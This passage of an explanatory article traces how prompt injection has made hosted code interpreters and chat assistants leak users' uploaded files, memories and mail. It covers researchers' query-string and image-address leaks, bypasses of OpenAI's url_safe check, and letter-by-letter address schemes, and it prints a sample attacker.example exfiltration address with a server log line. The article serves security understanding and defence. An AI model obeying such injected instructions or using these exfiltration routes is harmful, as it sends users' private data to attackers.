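# Prompt injection that makes hosted code interpreters send out users' files

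## Uploaded files, hosted interpreters and prompt injection

OpenAI's ChatGPT, Anthropic's Claude and several other chat assistants can write a program during a conversation, run it on the vendor's machines and use the result in the answer. This feature is called a hosted interpreter. People mostly use it on files they upload, such as sales figures, bank statements or survey responses. The program runs inside a sandbox, a container or virtual machine that isolates it from the vendor's other systems and from other customers.

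Since 2023 security researchers have shown that an outsider can use a hosted interpreter to steal the files that users upload to it. The outsider places instructions where the model will read them, such as in a web page or a shared document, and the model follows them, which is called prompt injection. The model then opens the user's file and sends its contents to a place that the outsider controls. Moving data out of a system to someone who is not entitled to it is called exfiltration. Researchers usually publish such an attack as a proof of concept, a demonstration on their own data. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) listed 17 exfiltration attacks on commercial AI products and wrote that the vendors had fixed almost all of them promptly. His list includes products without an interpreter, such as Slack. An interpreter adds private files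 and a machine that can process them.

### One request, from upload to answer

Suppose a user uploads a spreadsheet of customer orders to ChatGPT and asks which region grew fastest. The service copies the spreadsheet into an ordinary folder in the sandbox, where it stays until the session ends. The model then writes a short Python program that opens the file, adds up the orders by region and compares the totals, and the sandbox runs it. According to OpenAI's *Data analysis with ChatGPT*, the code runs in a Jupyter notebook, an environment that keeps its working data from one piece of code to the next, so a follow-up question can build on earlier results.

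Whatever the program prints goes back to the model as text. If the program fails, the model uses the error message to rewrite the code, a loop that Real Python's *OpenAI Code Interpreter* describes. Once it has a usable result, the model writes its answer, which the user's browser or app displays with any table or chart. Some responses include a "View Analysis" option for inspecting the code, according to University of Maine System's *ChatGPT* guide, but the answer appears whether or not the user opens it.

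Claude handles such a request in much the same way. Anthropic's *Code execution tool* describes the process for developers who use the model through a programming interface (an API) rather than the chat window. The developer uploads a file and refers to it in a message. Anthropic's servers run each command that Claude writes and return the output to Claude within the same request. Each request gets a new container unless the developer asks to reuse an earlier one.

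Several parts of this arrangement can send something to the outside world, and the known attacks differ in which part does the sending.

Code running in the sandbox can send files out itself if the sandbox lets it open network connections. The rules that limit this outgoing traffic are called egress controls. OpenAI states that ChatGPT's data-analysis environment cannot make external web requests, and Anthropic gives its API container no internet access. According to Anthropic's help page *Create and edit files with Claude*, the Claude app's interpreter has network access by default on the Free, Pro and Max plans, so that Claude can install software packages from approved sources. Access is off by default for new Enterprise customers, and the page lists the Team plan's default as both on and off. An allowlist blocks traffic to all but a set of permitted destinations, but an attacker may still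 be able to use one of those. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* documents an attack in which Claude's code sent files to the attacker's account through Anthropic's own file-upload service.

The browsing tool, which fetches web pages for the model and works separately from the sandbox, can also send data out. Each request gives the site the full web address, and OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that sites commonly keep these addresses in their logs. An attacker who gets the model to append private data to an address on their own site therefore only needs to read that site's log. The sandbox needs no network connection for this, because the code only reads the file, after which the model copies the result into an address and the browsing tool makes the request. File contents left ChatGPT inside a web address in a 2023 test, and new forms of the method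 still appear. In July 2026 Willison (2026) reported that a researcher, Ayush Paul, had led Claude's page-fetching tool through a series of links that spelled out a user's name letter by letter, and had also obtained the user's home city and employer. Anthropic has since closed that route.

The third sender is the user's own browser or mail program. When an answer contains an image stored on another site, the browser requests the image from that site as soon as it displays the answer, and the image's address can carry data just as a page's address can. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that works on a user's office files, had a version of this weakness in May 2026. It could email the user without asking for approval, and when the user opened a message from the agent, their software loaded external images. Willison describes how the requests for those images could reveal download links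 to the user's stored files.

Connectors link the assistant to other services, such as a cloud drive or a company database. Anthropic warns that they can carry network traffic regardless of the sandbox's egress setting.

### Why a model confuses data with instructions

A language model can obey an outsider because it receives all its input as one sequence of tokens, the word fragments it processes. That sequence includes the user's question, the vendor's standing instructions, the text of any fetched web page and the output of any program. If a program prints the first ten rows of the spreadsheet and one cell contains a sentence addressed to the model, that sentence joins the same sequence as the user's question.

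Schneier on Security's *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024) compares prompt injection with a flaw in the mid-twentieth-century telephone network, which carried voices and switching commands on the same line. A caller who whistled the right tones could operate the switch. AT&T fixed this by moving the commands to a separate channel. In SQL injection, a similar attack on databases, an attacker types a database command into a field meant for, say, a surname. Developers can stop it with parameterised queries, which make the database treat whatever is typed in the field as data and never as a command.

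In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C argues that comparing the two is dangerous because language models don't separate instructions from data. A database engine processes commands and stored values differently, whereas a model only predicts the next token from the text so far, so a fix has no built-in distinction to enforce. He thinks developers may never be able to eliminate prompt injection as they can SQL injection, and advises them to limit what a model can do if an injection succeeds.

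Vendors wrap each stretch of text in markers that label it as the user's message, the model's own reasoning or the output of a tool, and they train models to give these sources different degrees of authority. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether the labels work. They trained a classifier on a model's internal activity while it processed identical passages under different labels, so that the classifier could learn only the effect of the label. They then applied it to text whose style and label disagreed. Text that sounded like a user's request registered internally as one even when it was labelled as tool output. The model gave more weight to style, which an attacker controls, than to the label. This confusion also predicted behaviour. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent send out secret data, the success rate rose from 2% where measured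 confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

Researchers disagree somewhat about whether models can ever firmly separate instructions from data. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) treats this separation as an engineering goal and lists possible methods, including blocks of text that the model could read but never obey. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) leaves open whether separation is attainable and adds that it would not be enough, because false data can still corrupt an agent's actions, for example through the values it passes to a tool, even if the agent obeys no injected instructions. Fortune (2025) reported that OpenAI thinks prompt injection will probably never be fully solved. None of these sources claims that a working separation exists, so the disagreement matters little to someone uploading a file today.

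### Direct and indirect injection, and what carries it

OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* stresses that the instructions come from a third party, neither the user nor the AI. This separates prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which users try to get a model to break its rules. Willison, who named prompt injection after SQL injection, complains that people confuse the two. He says developers who do so tend to dismiss prompt injection, even though it harms the user, whereas a jailbreak embarrasses the vendor.

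An injection is indirect when it arrives in content that the model reads while working for the user. David C's example is a job applicant who puts invisible text in a CV telling the recruiter's AI system to approve the candidate. The applicant doesn't need access to that system. An injection is direct when it arrives in the user's own message. In February 2026, in a controlled exercise, a researcher at Anthropic emailed a colleague a ready-made prompt and asked them to run it. Along with routine setup steps, the prompt told Claude to read a file of passwords and send it to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*. The tool was Claude Code, which runs on the user's own computer rather than in a hosted sandbox, but a user can paste such a prompt into a hosted interpreter just as easily. The prompt gives the model few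 signs of an attack, because the request does come from the user.

Researchers have used many carriers for the attacker's text:

- Web pages. The security firm PromptArmor hid instructions in one-pixel type on a page that posed as a software guide, and Google's coding tool Antigravity followed them, as Willison reported in November 2025. A page can also show different text to different visitors. Paul's page displayed its instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude.
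- Documents with invisible text, in white or very small type. Fortune mentions a few words in a Google Doc that redirected the agent in OpenAI's Atlas browser.
- CSV files, which are tables saved as plain text. A cell can hold a sentence as easily as a number, and the sentence reaches the model when the program prints the rows.
- "Skill" files, packages of written instructions that a user adds to an assistant so that it can perform a particular task.
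- Custom GPTs, versions of ChatGPT that another person has set up with instructions and files of their own.
- Copied prompts, which users take from websites, forums or colleagues and paste into the message box.
- Links that pre-fill a prompt. The web address contains the text of a message, and the assistant's page opens with that message already in place.

Emails, support tickets and screenshots have also carried injections. A copied prompt or a pre-filled link produces a direct injection, while web pages, documents and CSV files produce indirect ones. Skill files and custom GPTs do not fit well into either category, because the assistant is supposed to follow the instructions in them. An attacker who writes one does not have to make the assistant treat data as a command, since the user has already authorized the instructions by installing the skill or opening the GPT.

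These attacks can be harder to spot than examples with hidden text and odd formatting suggest. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the most effective real attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, the persuasion con artists use on people, more than simple orders to ignore previous instructions. An attack can work in fully visible text if the malicious step seems plausible alongside the other instructions.

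### The lethal trifecta

Willison's June 2025 essay gives the most widely used account of when prompt injection leads to data theft. He names three capabilities that are dangerous only when combined, and calls the combination the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out.

A hosted interpreter easily ends up with private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. The private data includes the uploaded spreadsheet, any memories of earlier chats and any connected drives. Untrusted content comes in when the user asks the assistant to consult a web page or adds a document that somebody else wrote. Data can then leave through the code, the browsing tool, the user's browser or a connector, depending on which of them can send it out.

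The theft requires all three conditions, so removing any one prevents it. An assistant with no private data may obey the attacker but has nothing worth sending. If it reads only material that the user wrote, the attacker cannot give it instructions. If it cannot send anything out, it may open, copy and encode the file as instructed, but the copy stays in the session. The main attraction of this argument is that it does not depend on the model's judgement, since models are poor at telling instructions from data. It covers only theft, and an injected instruction can still falsify an answer or delete a file inside the sandbox.

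In practice, some of the three are easier to remove than others. Private data is the reason people use the feature, and untrusted content is hard to keep out because it includes almost anything the user did not write. Willison therefore regards the route for sending data out as generally the easiest to remove, and most of the vendor fixes he had recorded by mid-2025 closed one such route. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, an optional ChatGPT setting, takes the same approach by limiting outbound network requests, but it also disables or restricts some useful features.

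However, blocking one route for sending data removes a leg of the trifecta only if the other routes are blocked too. Anthropic tells customers that switching off the sandbox's network access "eliminates this risk entirely", which seems reasonable for data sent by the code. But it notes on the same page that connectors keep working. The setting also covers only the sandbox, whereas the Copilot Cowork leak went through an image on the user's own screen.

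### How this differs from a sandbox escape

One way data can leak from a sandbox is a sandbox escape, in which code inside the container exploits a flaw in the isolation and gains control of the host machine. From there it may reach other customers' sessions. Vendors work hard to prevent this. In the chat app, Claude's code runs in a separate container for each session under gVisor, software that sits between a program and the host's operating system. Anthropic says this is meant to protect its own infrastructure and keep its customers isolated from one another.

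An attacker can steal an uploaded file without exploiting a flaw in the sandbox. The user has already put the file there for the code to read, so the code can open it with ordinary permissions and send the data out by a route that the product allows. Anthropic says in its help page for Cowork, its agent for general office work, that isolation protects the user's computer from the code that Claude runs but does not change what Claude can read or do with the access it has. After researchers took files out of Cowork through a permitted domain, the company's engineers said, "The sandbox worked perfectly, and yet the data was exfiltrated."

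Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, written about Claude Code, describes a sandbox as restricting both the files a program can touch and the network destinations it can reach. It states that with both restrictions in place, even a successful injection stays fully isolated. The Cowork case shows that network isolation contains an injection only if an attacker cannot use any destination on the permitted list. That depends on what each destination's services allow, regardless of how strong the container is. According to Anthropic, the established isolation software across its products has proved dependable, and the part that failed was the allowlist proxy it had built itself, the program that checked where outgoing traffic was headed.

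The two attacks also leave different traces. An escape has to make the isolation software do something it should never do, which an investigator can look for. Anthropic's engineers observe that when a poisoned document or web page gets an agent to send data out, the log shows only a successful, authorised request.

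## ChatGPT in 2023: file contents sent inside a web address

The earliest documented way to get an uploaded file out of ChatGPT used an ordinary request for a web page. A web address can end in a question mark followed by extra text, called the query string, which websites use for purposes such as receiving a visitor's search terms. The site's log usually records the whole address, so whoever runs the site can read the query string.

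Suppose a user has uploaded a file with two lines, `name,total` and `Lee & Co,85`. Some characters, including spaces and line breaks, cannot appear in an address, and others, such as the ampersand, have a special meaning there. URL encoding replaces them with codes that begin with a percent sign. An attacker who runs a site at attacker.example wants ChatGPT to encode the two lines and request this address:

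`attacker.example/data?d=name%2Ctotal%0ALee%20%26%20Co%2C85`

Here %0A stands for the line break and %26 for the ampersand. When the request arrives, the server adds a line like this to its log:

`14/Nov/2023 10:32:07 "GET /data?d=name%2Ctotal%0ALee%20%26%20Co%2C85" 200`

A GET request fetches a page, and 200 means that the server answered it. The attacker decodes the data in the address to recover the file. The page can be blank, because the data is sent in the request.

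The security researcher Johann Rehberger published real log entries of this kind from September 2023 in *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red. One entry contains the opening of a test conversation in which a user introduces herself as Alice and says she likes finance and cookies.

### The Tom's Hardware test

Rehberger reported on Twitter that ChatGPT would send out uploaded files in this way. Avram Piltch, an editor at the technology site Tom's Hardware, then reproduced the attack with a paid ChatGPT Plus account and described it there in *ChatGPT's New Code Interpreter Has Giant Security Hole*. The article almost certainly dates from mid-November 2023. Windows Central's *ChatGPT's new code interpreting tool could become a hacker's paradise* embeds a post of 10 November that appears to be Rehberger's, and Fanatical Futurist's *Security and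 Privacy* (2023) cited Piltch's test on 22 November.

Piltch made a file called env_vars.txt that contained a fake password and a fake API key, a secret string that identifies the account making a request to a service. Programmers often keep real credentials in such a file while they test a script, and might upload it with the script when they ask for help. He uploaded the file to a new chat with GPT-4. ChatGPT kept uploads in a folder called /mnt/data and listed the folder's contents when he asked.

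Piltch then put a page with a weather forecast on his own website. The page also contained instructions to encode everything in /mnt/data as one long line and send that line to his server in a query string. He pasted the page's address into the chat. ChatGPT summarised the weather and also carried out the instructions. Piltch found a new text file on his server that contained the planted credentials.

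Piltch repeated the attack, with some variations, over a few days. In some chats ChatGPT sent the data immediately. In others it displayed the address as a link and sent no data until he clicked it. Sometimes it refused to open any outside page, or said it was not allowed to transmit data from files this way. When it would not open pages, starting a new chat solved the problem. The attack also worked after he uploaded a CSV file for analysis, which is a more typical upload than a file of passwords.

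Piltch writes that the attack worked "a lot of the time, but not always" and gives no counts, so readers cannot calculate a success rate from his test. The test does show that the theft was possible on the live product, with an ordinary account and without special skill.

### Which part of ChatGPT sent the data

The sandbox held the files but probably did not send them, although Piltch describes the sandbox itself as wide open to these attacks. OpenAI said in the feature's launch announcement, *ChatGPT plugins*, that it used strict network controls to stop executed code from reaching the internet, and the same rule appears in its current documentation. A blogger's tests from inside the sandbox, described in *Secrets of the ChatGPT Linux system*, support OpenAI's claim. The blogger found one incoming connection, from the system that runs ChatGPT, and could not open any outgoing connections.

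The browsing tool did have access to the web. OpenAI had limited its original browsing plugin to GET requests, so the model could retrieve pages but not submit forms or buy things. OpenAI wrote that this reduced certain risks without eliminating them. The limit did little to prevent data theft, since a GET request can carry data in the query string of its web address.

Most likely, code in the sandbox read and encoded Piltch's file, and the browsing tool sent it. In the chats where ChatGPT displayed a link, Piltch's browser made the request when he clicked it. He does not report checking which component contacted his server, so this explanation is based on what OpenAI allowed each component to do.

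Rehberger had demonstrated almost the same sequence in May 2023 with email in place of files. He used two plugins, add-ons that connected ChatGPT to outside services. WebPilot fetched a page containing his instructions, and Zapier retrieved the latest message from a Gmail account. ChatGPT condensed the message to 20 words, encoded the result and appended it to a web address, which WebPilot then loaded. Willison, in *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, called it the first working demonstration he had seen of private data leaving through ChatGPT plugins. This way of sending data out was therefore at least six months old when Piltch ran his test. File uploads gave attackers more data to send, and the interpreter was a convenient tool for reading and encoding it.

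### Links and images

Piltch sometimes had to click a link, and an earlier attack also depended on the user doing so. In February 2023 Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, in *Not what you've signed up for*, designed an injection that made a chatbot coax users into revealing their real names and then into clicking a link whose address contained the name. They tried it on a synthetic application and on Microsoft's Bing Chat. Bing Chat could hide the link's address behind harmless words. It also kept to the injected task over several turns, so it could ask again later if a user did not give a name at first.

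Images don't need a click, because the browser requests them automatically. ChatGPT writes its answers in Markdown, which uses a short piece of text containing a web address to represent an image, so an attacker only had to get the model to write that text with data in the address. Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, discovered this vulnerability in late March 2023, and Willison drew attention to it on 14 April in a post named after Samoilenko's paper.

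Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes an attack through copied text. When a visitor copied a passage from the attacker's website, a script added instructions to the end of it. A visitor who didn't look closely could then paste the instructions into ChatGPT along with the passage. The instructions were to end the answer with a transparent, one-pixel image whose address contained something from the conversation. In one example, this was login code that ChatGPT had just corrected for the user. A longer version called for the same image at the end of every later answer, so that each new question also reached the attacker's server.

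Samoilenko acknowledged that the model's output varied between attempts and that the same instructions sometimes failed. If ChatGPT responded slowly, the user could also see the strange address appear on the screen. He found it easy to extract the user's earlier questions or code, but very difficult to extract passwords or API keys. Piltch later extracted such a secret from an uploaded file, but he used GPT-4, which Samoilenko had listed as still to be tried. The results may differ because of the models, or because taking a secret from a conversation is different from taking a whole file regardless of its contents.

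Rehberger found the image leak independently a few days after Samoilenko, whom he credits in *ChatGPT Plugins: Data Exfiltration via Images*. In his version, a plugin fetched a web page containing the instructions, so the user did not have to paste poisoned text. ChatGPT then summarised the conversation so far and sent the summary out in an image's address.

A web address can hold only a limited amount of text, so the attack works only on short files or extracts. In September 2023 Rehberger found a way around this limit for conversations. His instructions made ChatGPT use whatever plugin was available to turn the whole chat into a document, diagram or narrated video on an outside service. The plugin returned a link to the result, and the image's address had to contain only that link. Two of the log entries he published show requests labelled as coming from Firefox, which is consistent with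 the user's own browser sending them while it displayed the answer.

Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024) lists eleven products in which he had found and reported the image leak, including Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat. He also describes how link previews can leak data without a click. Slack, Discord and Teams fetch a page to preview it as soon as its address appears in a message, so a chatbot that posts in one of them can send data out by writing the address. OpenAI began to check image addresses in ChatGPT's web version in December 2023, according to Rehberger's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* on Embrace The Red.

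### GPTs that shared one user's files

In Piltch's test, the stolen file and the malicious page were in the same chat. During the same period, ChatGPT had a flaw that made files from other chats accessible. Rehberger reported it to OpenAI in early November 2023 and published it more than 90 days later, in early 2024, in Embrace The Red's *Lack of Isolation between Code Interpreter sessions of GPTs*.

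The flaw was that a user's ordinary ChatGPT chats and all the custom GPTs they used shared one container. Each user had a separate container, so one customer could not see another's files. Rehberger uploaded a file in a normal chat, then opened somebody else's GPT with the interpreter switched on and asked it to list /mnt/data. His file was there, and the GPT could read or overwrite it. The container's network name was also the same in both chats. Someone who analysed their bank transactions in ChatGPT and then tried a stranger's GPT could have exposed the transactions to it, unless the container had reset first. The container reset after some idle time, but Rehberger could not establish how long, and users had no button to reset it themselves.

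Files belonging to people who built GPTs were also exposed. Builders could attach reference documents to a GPT, which ChatGPT copied into the shared folder as soon as the interpreter ran. *GPT Store Mining and Analysis* (2024) describes a test in which researchers opened several GPTs in turn, each with documents attached, and listed the folder in each. The last GPT had access to the documents of all the others. The researchers concluded that careful instructions in one GPT could not protect its documents if the same user also opened a badly written or malicious one.

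Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *A New Era in LLM Security*, also found that a file uploaded in one ChatGPT session was accessible from another. Piltch had written that each chat created a new virtual machine, but Rehberger's evidence is stronger because he compared the containers directly and two other groups saw files carry over between sessions.

A malicious GPT's code could read the file in the shared container, but the contents still had to reach the GPT's builder through an image, a link or some other connection. Images would have worked until OpenAI introduced its checks. In December 2023, the day before he noticed the checks, Rehberger tested a GPT built for data theft on a consenting volunteer and received details of the conversation on his server.

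Rehberger had advised OpenAI to give every GPT session its own container. By the time he published, the company had switched the interpreter off by default in new GPTs. This helped builders who never turned it on but did not change existing GPTs. OpenAI fixed the underlying flaw in May 2024, according to an update to Rehberger's post.

### How likely an attack was

Piltch asked whether anyone would fall victim to this outside a test. The user had to paste in the address of a page that contained malicious instructions and, in many cases, then click a link. He suggested that an attacker could add instructions to a page people already trusted, through a comment or an infected add-on to the site's software, or could persuade someone to paste in the address of a malicious page. He concluded that the security hole should not exist, however far-fetched an attack might seem.

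Some of these conditions were less restrictive than they appeared. Asking for a summary of a web page was a normal use of ChatGPT, and Samoilenko's method worked on people who had only copied a paragraph. The image variant needed no click, although Piltch did not test it on uploaded files. Until May 2024, the file could be in a different chat. Wu and colleagues combined several of these weaknesses in an attack on chat histories. The user only had to ask ChatGPT to open a page that the researchers had published.

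Other difficulties were greater for a real attacker than for Piltch. When ChatGPT refused, he could open a new chat and try again, whereas an attacker had to wait for the user to come back. He also knew that /mnt/data held a file worth taking, while instructions planted on a public page would mostly have reached people who had uploaded nothing. The method suited an attacker who could wait for a few successes or persuade a particular person to open a page. Rehberger, Samoilenko and Piltch describe only tests on their own data or with a volunteer, and none reports a theft from an actual user.

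These tests describe ChatGPT as it was in 2023 and early 2024, but a query string could still carry data out of a later version. In February 2026, Yang, Na and Choi recorded a fictitious birth date in their server log after ChatGPT 5.2 put it in a web address (*An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection*, 2026). They had not supplied the date in an uploaded file.

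## Rules about which web addresses an assistant may open

OpenAI introduced its check on image addresses about eight months after it first received a report of the leak. Since then OpenAI and Anthropic have both set rules about which web addresses an assistant may open on its own. The rules make it hard for a model to write private data into an address. Researchers who got around them mostly had the model pick from addresses the rules already allowed.

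### The url_safe check

Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web page sent the image's address to an OpenAI service called url_safe, and the browser requested the image only if the service classified the address as safe. Rehberger, who described the check on Embrace The Red, tried an address on his own site with an email address in the query string. The service rejected it, and ChatGPT did not display the image.

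The check ran in the web page, so OpenAI had to build it separately into every other version of ChatGPT. The iPhone app lacked it in December 2023, and Rehberger also found it missing from the macOS app.

OpenAI did not publish the criteria for url_safe. Microsoft had stopped the same leak in Bing Chat in May 2023 with a Content-Security-Policy, a list that tells the browser which sites a page may load content from. Anyone can read such a list, but url_safe ran on OpenAI's servers, so researchers had to test it from outside. Rehberger put 36 images on his site, one for each letter and digit, and nine of their addresses passed. He could not tell why the address for "a" passed and the one for "d" did not, but he still managed to send himself the word "hi" in two requests.

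*From ChatBot To SpyBot*, written by the security company Imperva soon after ChatGPT gained its memory feature, describes ChatGPT's check on web addresses as essentially a text search. ChatGPT could display an image or open a page if the address already appeared in the conversation. This blocked an address that ended in the contents of a file, because the model had only just composed it. But the search also covered the user's custom instructions, a standing note that ChatGPT reads in every chat. An attacker who planted text there could list an address for each letter and digit in advance, and the model could then request them in the order that spelled out a password.

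Imperva found that one long address could replace the list. Its path contained the digits and the alphabet, and the model cut it off at the character to be sent. The check accepted any fragment of the conversation, so every shortened version passed. It also accepted bare domain names, so an attacker could register a separate domain for each character. At Imperva's estimate of $1 to $2 per domain, all 36 would cost $36 to $72. These findings don't explain why only nine of Rehberger's addresses passed. OpenAI may have changed the check between the two tests.

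### Trusted domains that anyone could use

url_safe was less strict with some well-known domains. Imperva found that it accepted any address on openai.com, for example, and suggested that an attacker could exploit an address on such a domain that immediately redirects visitors to another site.

Tenable, another security company, found redirects of this kind on bing.com, which always passed the check. Each Bing search result has a tracking link on bing.com that forwards the visitor to the listed page, so any page in Bing's index also has a trusted address. An attacker cannot add data to a tracking link, so Tenable had Bing index one page for each letter of the alphabet. ChatGPT could then spell out a word by displaying the corresponding links as images. Tenable reported this on 10 December 2024 and kept asking for updates until at least March 2025. OpenAI had not fixed the flaw when Tenable's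 *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* appeared.

Tenable had to get past another defence to steal anything with these links. Its *HackedGPT* (November 2025) describes how ChatGPT hands web pages to a second model, SearchGPT, which cannot see the user's memories or conversation. Instructions on a page can take over SearchGPT, but it has nothing worth stealing. Tenable posted a blog comment containing instructions that made SearchGPT end its summary with further instructions for ChatGPT. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT reread the conversation, followed the instructions and displayed the images. A bug in how ChatGPT's site displayed code blocks hid the added text from the user.

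Rehberger found a larger gap in the check, which also trusted windows.net, a domain Microsoft uses for Azure cloud storage. Anyone can open a storage account there and read the log of requests made to it. An attacker could therefore have ChatGPT put whole passages of text into a single address, as in 2023, instead of spelling them out. In a demonstration, a PDF with hidden instructions made ChatGPT send Rehberger the user's recent chat history. He had reported the gap in October 2024, and it was still open when he published Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* in 2025. He also found a similar problem with apache.org. He asked OpenAI to publish its list of safe domains and let business customers change it.

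In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger writes that OpenAI tightened url_safe around August 2025 and that the change stopped the attacks he had published. The change may not have covered every route at first, because Tenable shows its blog-comment attack working in ChatGPT 5, which OpenAI released that August. Tenable does not date the test.

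### OpenAI's public-address rule

In January 2026, when OpenAI explained the rule it now uses, it said it had considered a list of trusted sites and rejected the idea for two reasons. First, many legitimate sites contain redirects, so data can still reach an attacker if only the first domain is checked. Tenable had used bing.com in this way, although OpenAI does not mention the case. Second, a strict list would produce frequent warnings about harmless sites, and people would learn to click through them. The windows.net case adds a third reason, which OpenAI does not give. A trustworthy company's domain may host pages and logs belonging to strangers.

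OpenAI lets ChatGPT load a page or an image automatically only if a crawler has already recorded its exact address. The crawler, a program that follows links across the public web, has no access to conversations, accounts or other user data. If the address is not in the crawler's records, the system either tells the model to try another site or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. The user can still open the link after seeing the warning.

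The address in the 2023 example ended in the encoded order of a customer called Lee & Co. The model composed this address during the conversation, so the crawler could not have seen it beforehand. ChatGPT would therefore not load it automatically, whether it was on attacker.example or on a storage account at windows.net.

OpenAI claims only that the rule keeps an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself. A user who dismisses the warning can still send the data. OpenAI does not promise that a page's content is trustworthy or free of malicious instructions, and it describes the rule as one layer among several. The announcement includes no figures on how often ordinary browsing triggers a warning or how many attacks the rule stops.

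The rule depends on the crawler being independent of users, which OpenAI can arrange. It also assumes that an already public address reveals little about the person whose assistant opens it. OpenAI says such an address is "much less likely" to contain private data, which is reasonable for the text of the address, but the attacker can also learn something from which public address the model chose. Rehberger reports that OpenAI's more detailed paper on the rule, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges this weakness.

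ChatGPT probably also makes an exception for addresses in the user's own messages. Rehberger understands that it treats any such address as safe for the rest of the chat. This makes sense when a user asks for a summary of a particular page, but it is less safe when the user pastes in a prompt from a website, since the attacker may have written the addresses in it.

### How much fixed addresses can carry

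Suppose an attacker has 36 public pages, one for each letter and digit, and the crawler has recorded all of them. The attacker's instructions tell the model to open the pages in the order that spells a secret. Every address passes the rule, and the attacker reads the secret from the order of the requests in the server's log.

With this method, a request that could go to any of *n* addresses carries log₂ *n* bits, and *k* requests in a known order carry *k* times as much. With 36 addresses, each request carries about 5.2 bits. Sending a nine-digit number, such as a US Social Security number, takes nine requests if each request encodes one digit. A more efficient code would take only six, because six requests allow about 2.2 billion combinations, more than the one billion possible nine-digit numbers.

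An attacker with more addresses needs fewer requests. With 1,000 pages, each could stand for three digits, and three requests would be enough. Rehberger points out that a fairly large blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, and that an attacker could build a vocabulary of thousands of addresses and define it in the injected instructions. An attacker looking for a four-digit PIN could assign each possible PIN to one of 10,000 pages and learn the PIN from a single request.

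Whole files are much harder to steal this way. The two-line file from the 2023 example has 22 characters, including a line break, and would take 22 requests, with extra addresses for punctuation and spaces. A spreadsheet of 10,000 bytes would take about 15,500 requests with 36 addresses, or about 8,000 with 1,000 addresses. Even if the hosted interpreter compressed the file first, sending it would probably still take thousands of requests. For uploaded files, the rule mainly protects bulk data, because a password, an account number or one line of a salary table is still short enough to send.

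The model also has to spell the secret correctly, and each additional request is another chance to make a mistake. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested this on a system that ran entirely on the researchers' own machines and previewed web addresses automatically. Malicious instructions caused an unintended outgoing request about 89% of the time. Splitting the secret across several requests reduced the researchers' main measure of leakage by 73%. They still regard splitting as a serious threat, because a defence that inspects each request separately may not detect it. An interpreter could make the spelling more reliable, since a short program can turn text into the correct list of addresses.

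### ZombieAgent

The security company Radware showed that character-by-character theft could work on ChatGPT when it was connected to a user's Gmail account. In an earlier attack, ShadowLeak, Radware had used a single crafted email to make ChatGPT's Deep Research agent add inbox data to a web address. OpenAI responded by allowing ChatGPT to open addresses only exactly as it had received them, as Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* explains.

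Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the researcher Zvika Babo got around this restriction. He sent an email containing a ready-made address for each letter and digit, plus one for spaces. When the user later asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail, ChatGPT read the email, found the information it asked for and opened the addresses that spelled it out, one character at a time. OpenAI's servers made the requests, so the user saw nothing in the browser and an employer's network monitoring would not have detected them.

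Requests can arrive out of order, so Babo also numbered the addresses by position. The letter "a" had one address for the first place in the secret, another for the second, and so on. A block of nine characters needs nine versions of each address, or 324 addresses for the 36 letters and digits. Radware says it sent OpenAI an improved version with a 100% success rate, but it does not give the number of trials.

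Radware also made the theft continue across chats. OpenAI had blocked ChatGPT from using its memory after it had used a connector in the same chat, but not from using a connector after its memory. A malicious file that the user shared with ChatGPT could therefore store a rule in its memory to read the attacker's email and follow its instructions before every answer. In another version, ChatGPT sent out addresses from the user's inbox, and the attacker's server forwarded the malicious email to them. Radware took data from mail and ChatGPT's memory, but did not demonstrate the theft of a file that a user had uploaded for analysis.

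Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. A press account, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, says that OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from opening links found in emails unless the addresses are in a well-known public index. OpenAI announced a similar rule six weeks later. Such a rule stops an attacker from inventing addresses on a new site and using them the same day, but an attacker who first gets the pages indexed could still try the same code.

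### Links inside pages that Claude fetched

Anthropic chose a rule based on where an address comes from. Willison reported in *Claude API* that Anthropic added web_fetch, a tool that retrieves pages, to Claude's programming interface in September 2025 and banned Claude from using it to open addresses it composes itself. Claude could open an exact address that the user had entered or that its search tool had returned. In its documentation, Anthropic still warned developers about exfiltration and advised them to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data.

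The rule blocks an instruction to append a user's answers to an address and open it. But web_fetch could also follow links on pages it had already fetched, and Willison (2026) explained in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that this made Ayush Paul's letter-by-letter attack of July 2026 possible. Paul built a fake coffee-shop site, where he told Claude that it had to identify its user before it could enter. He instructed Claude to find the user's profile by clicking through the alphabet, and blamed this odd procedure on the limits of web_fetch. Claude opened the page for the first letter of the name, which had links for the second letter, and continued from there.

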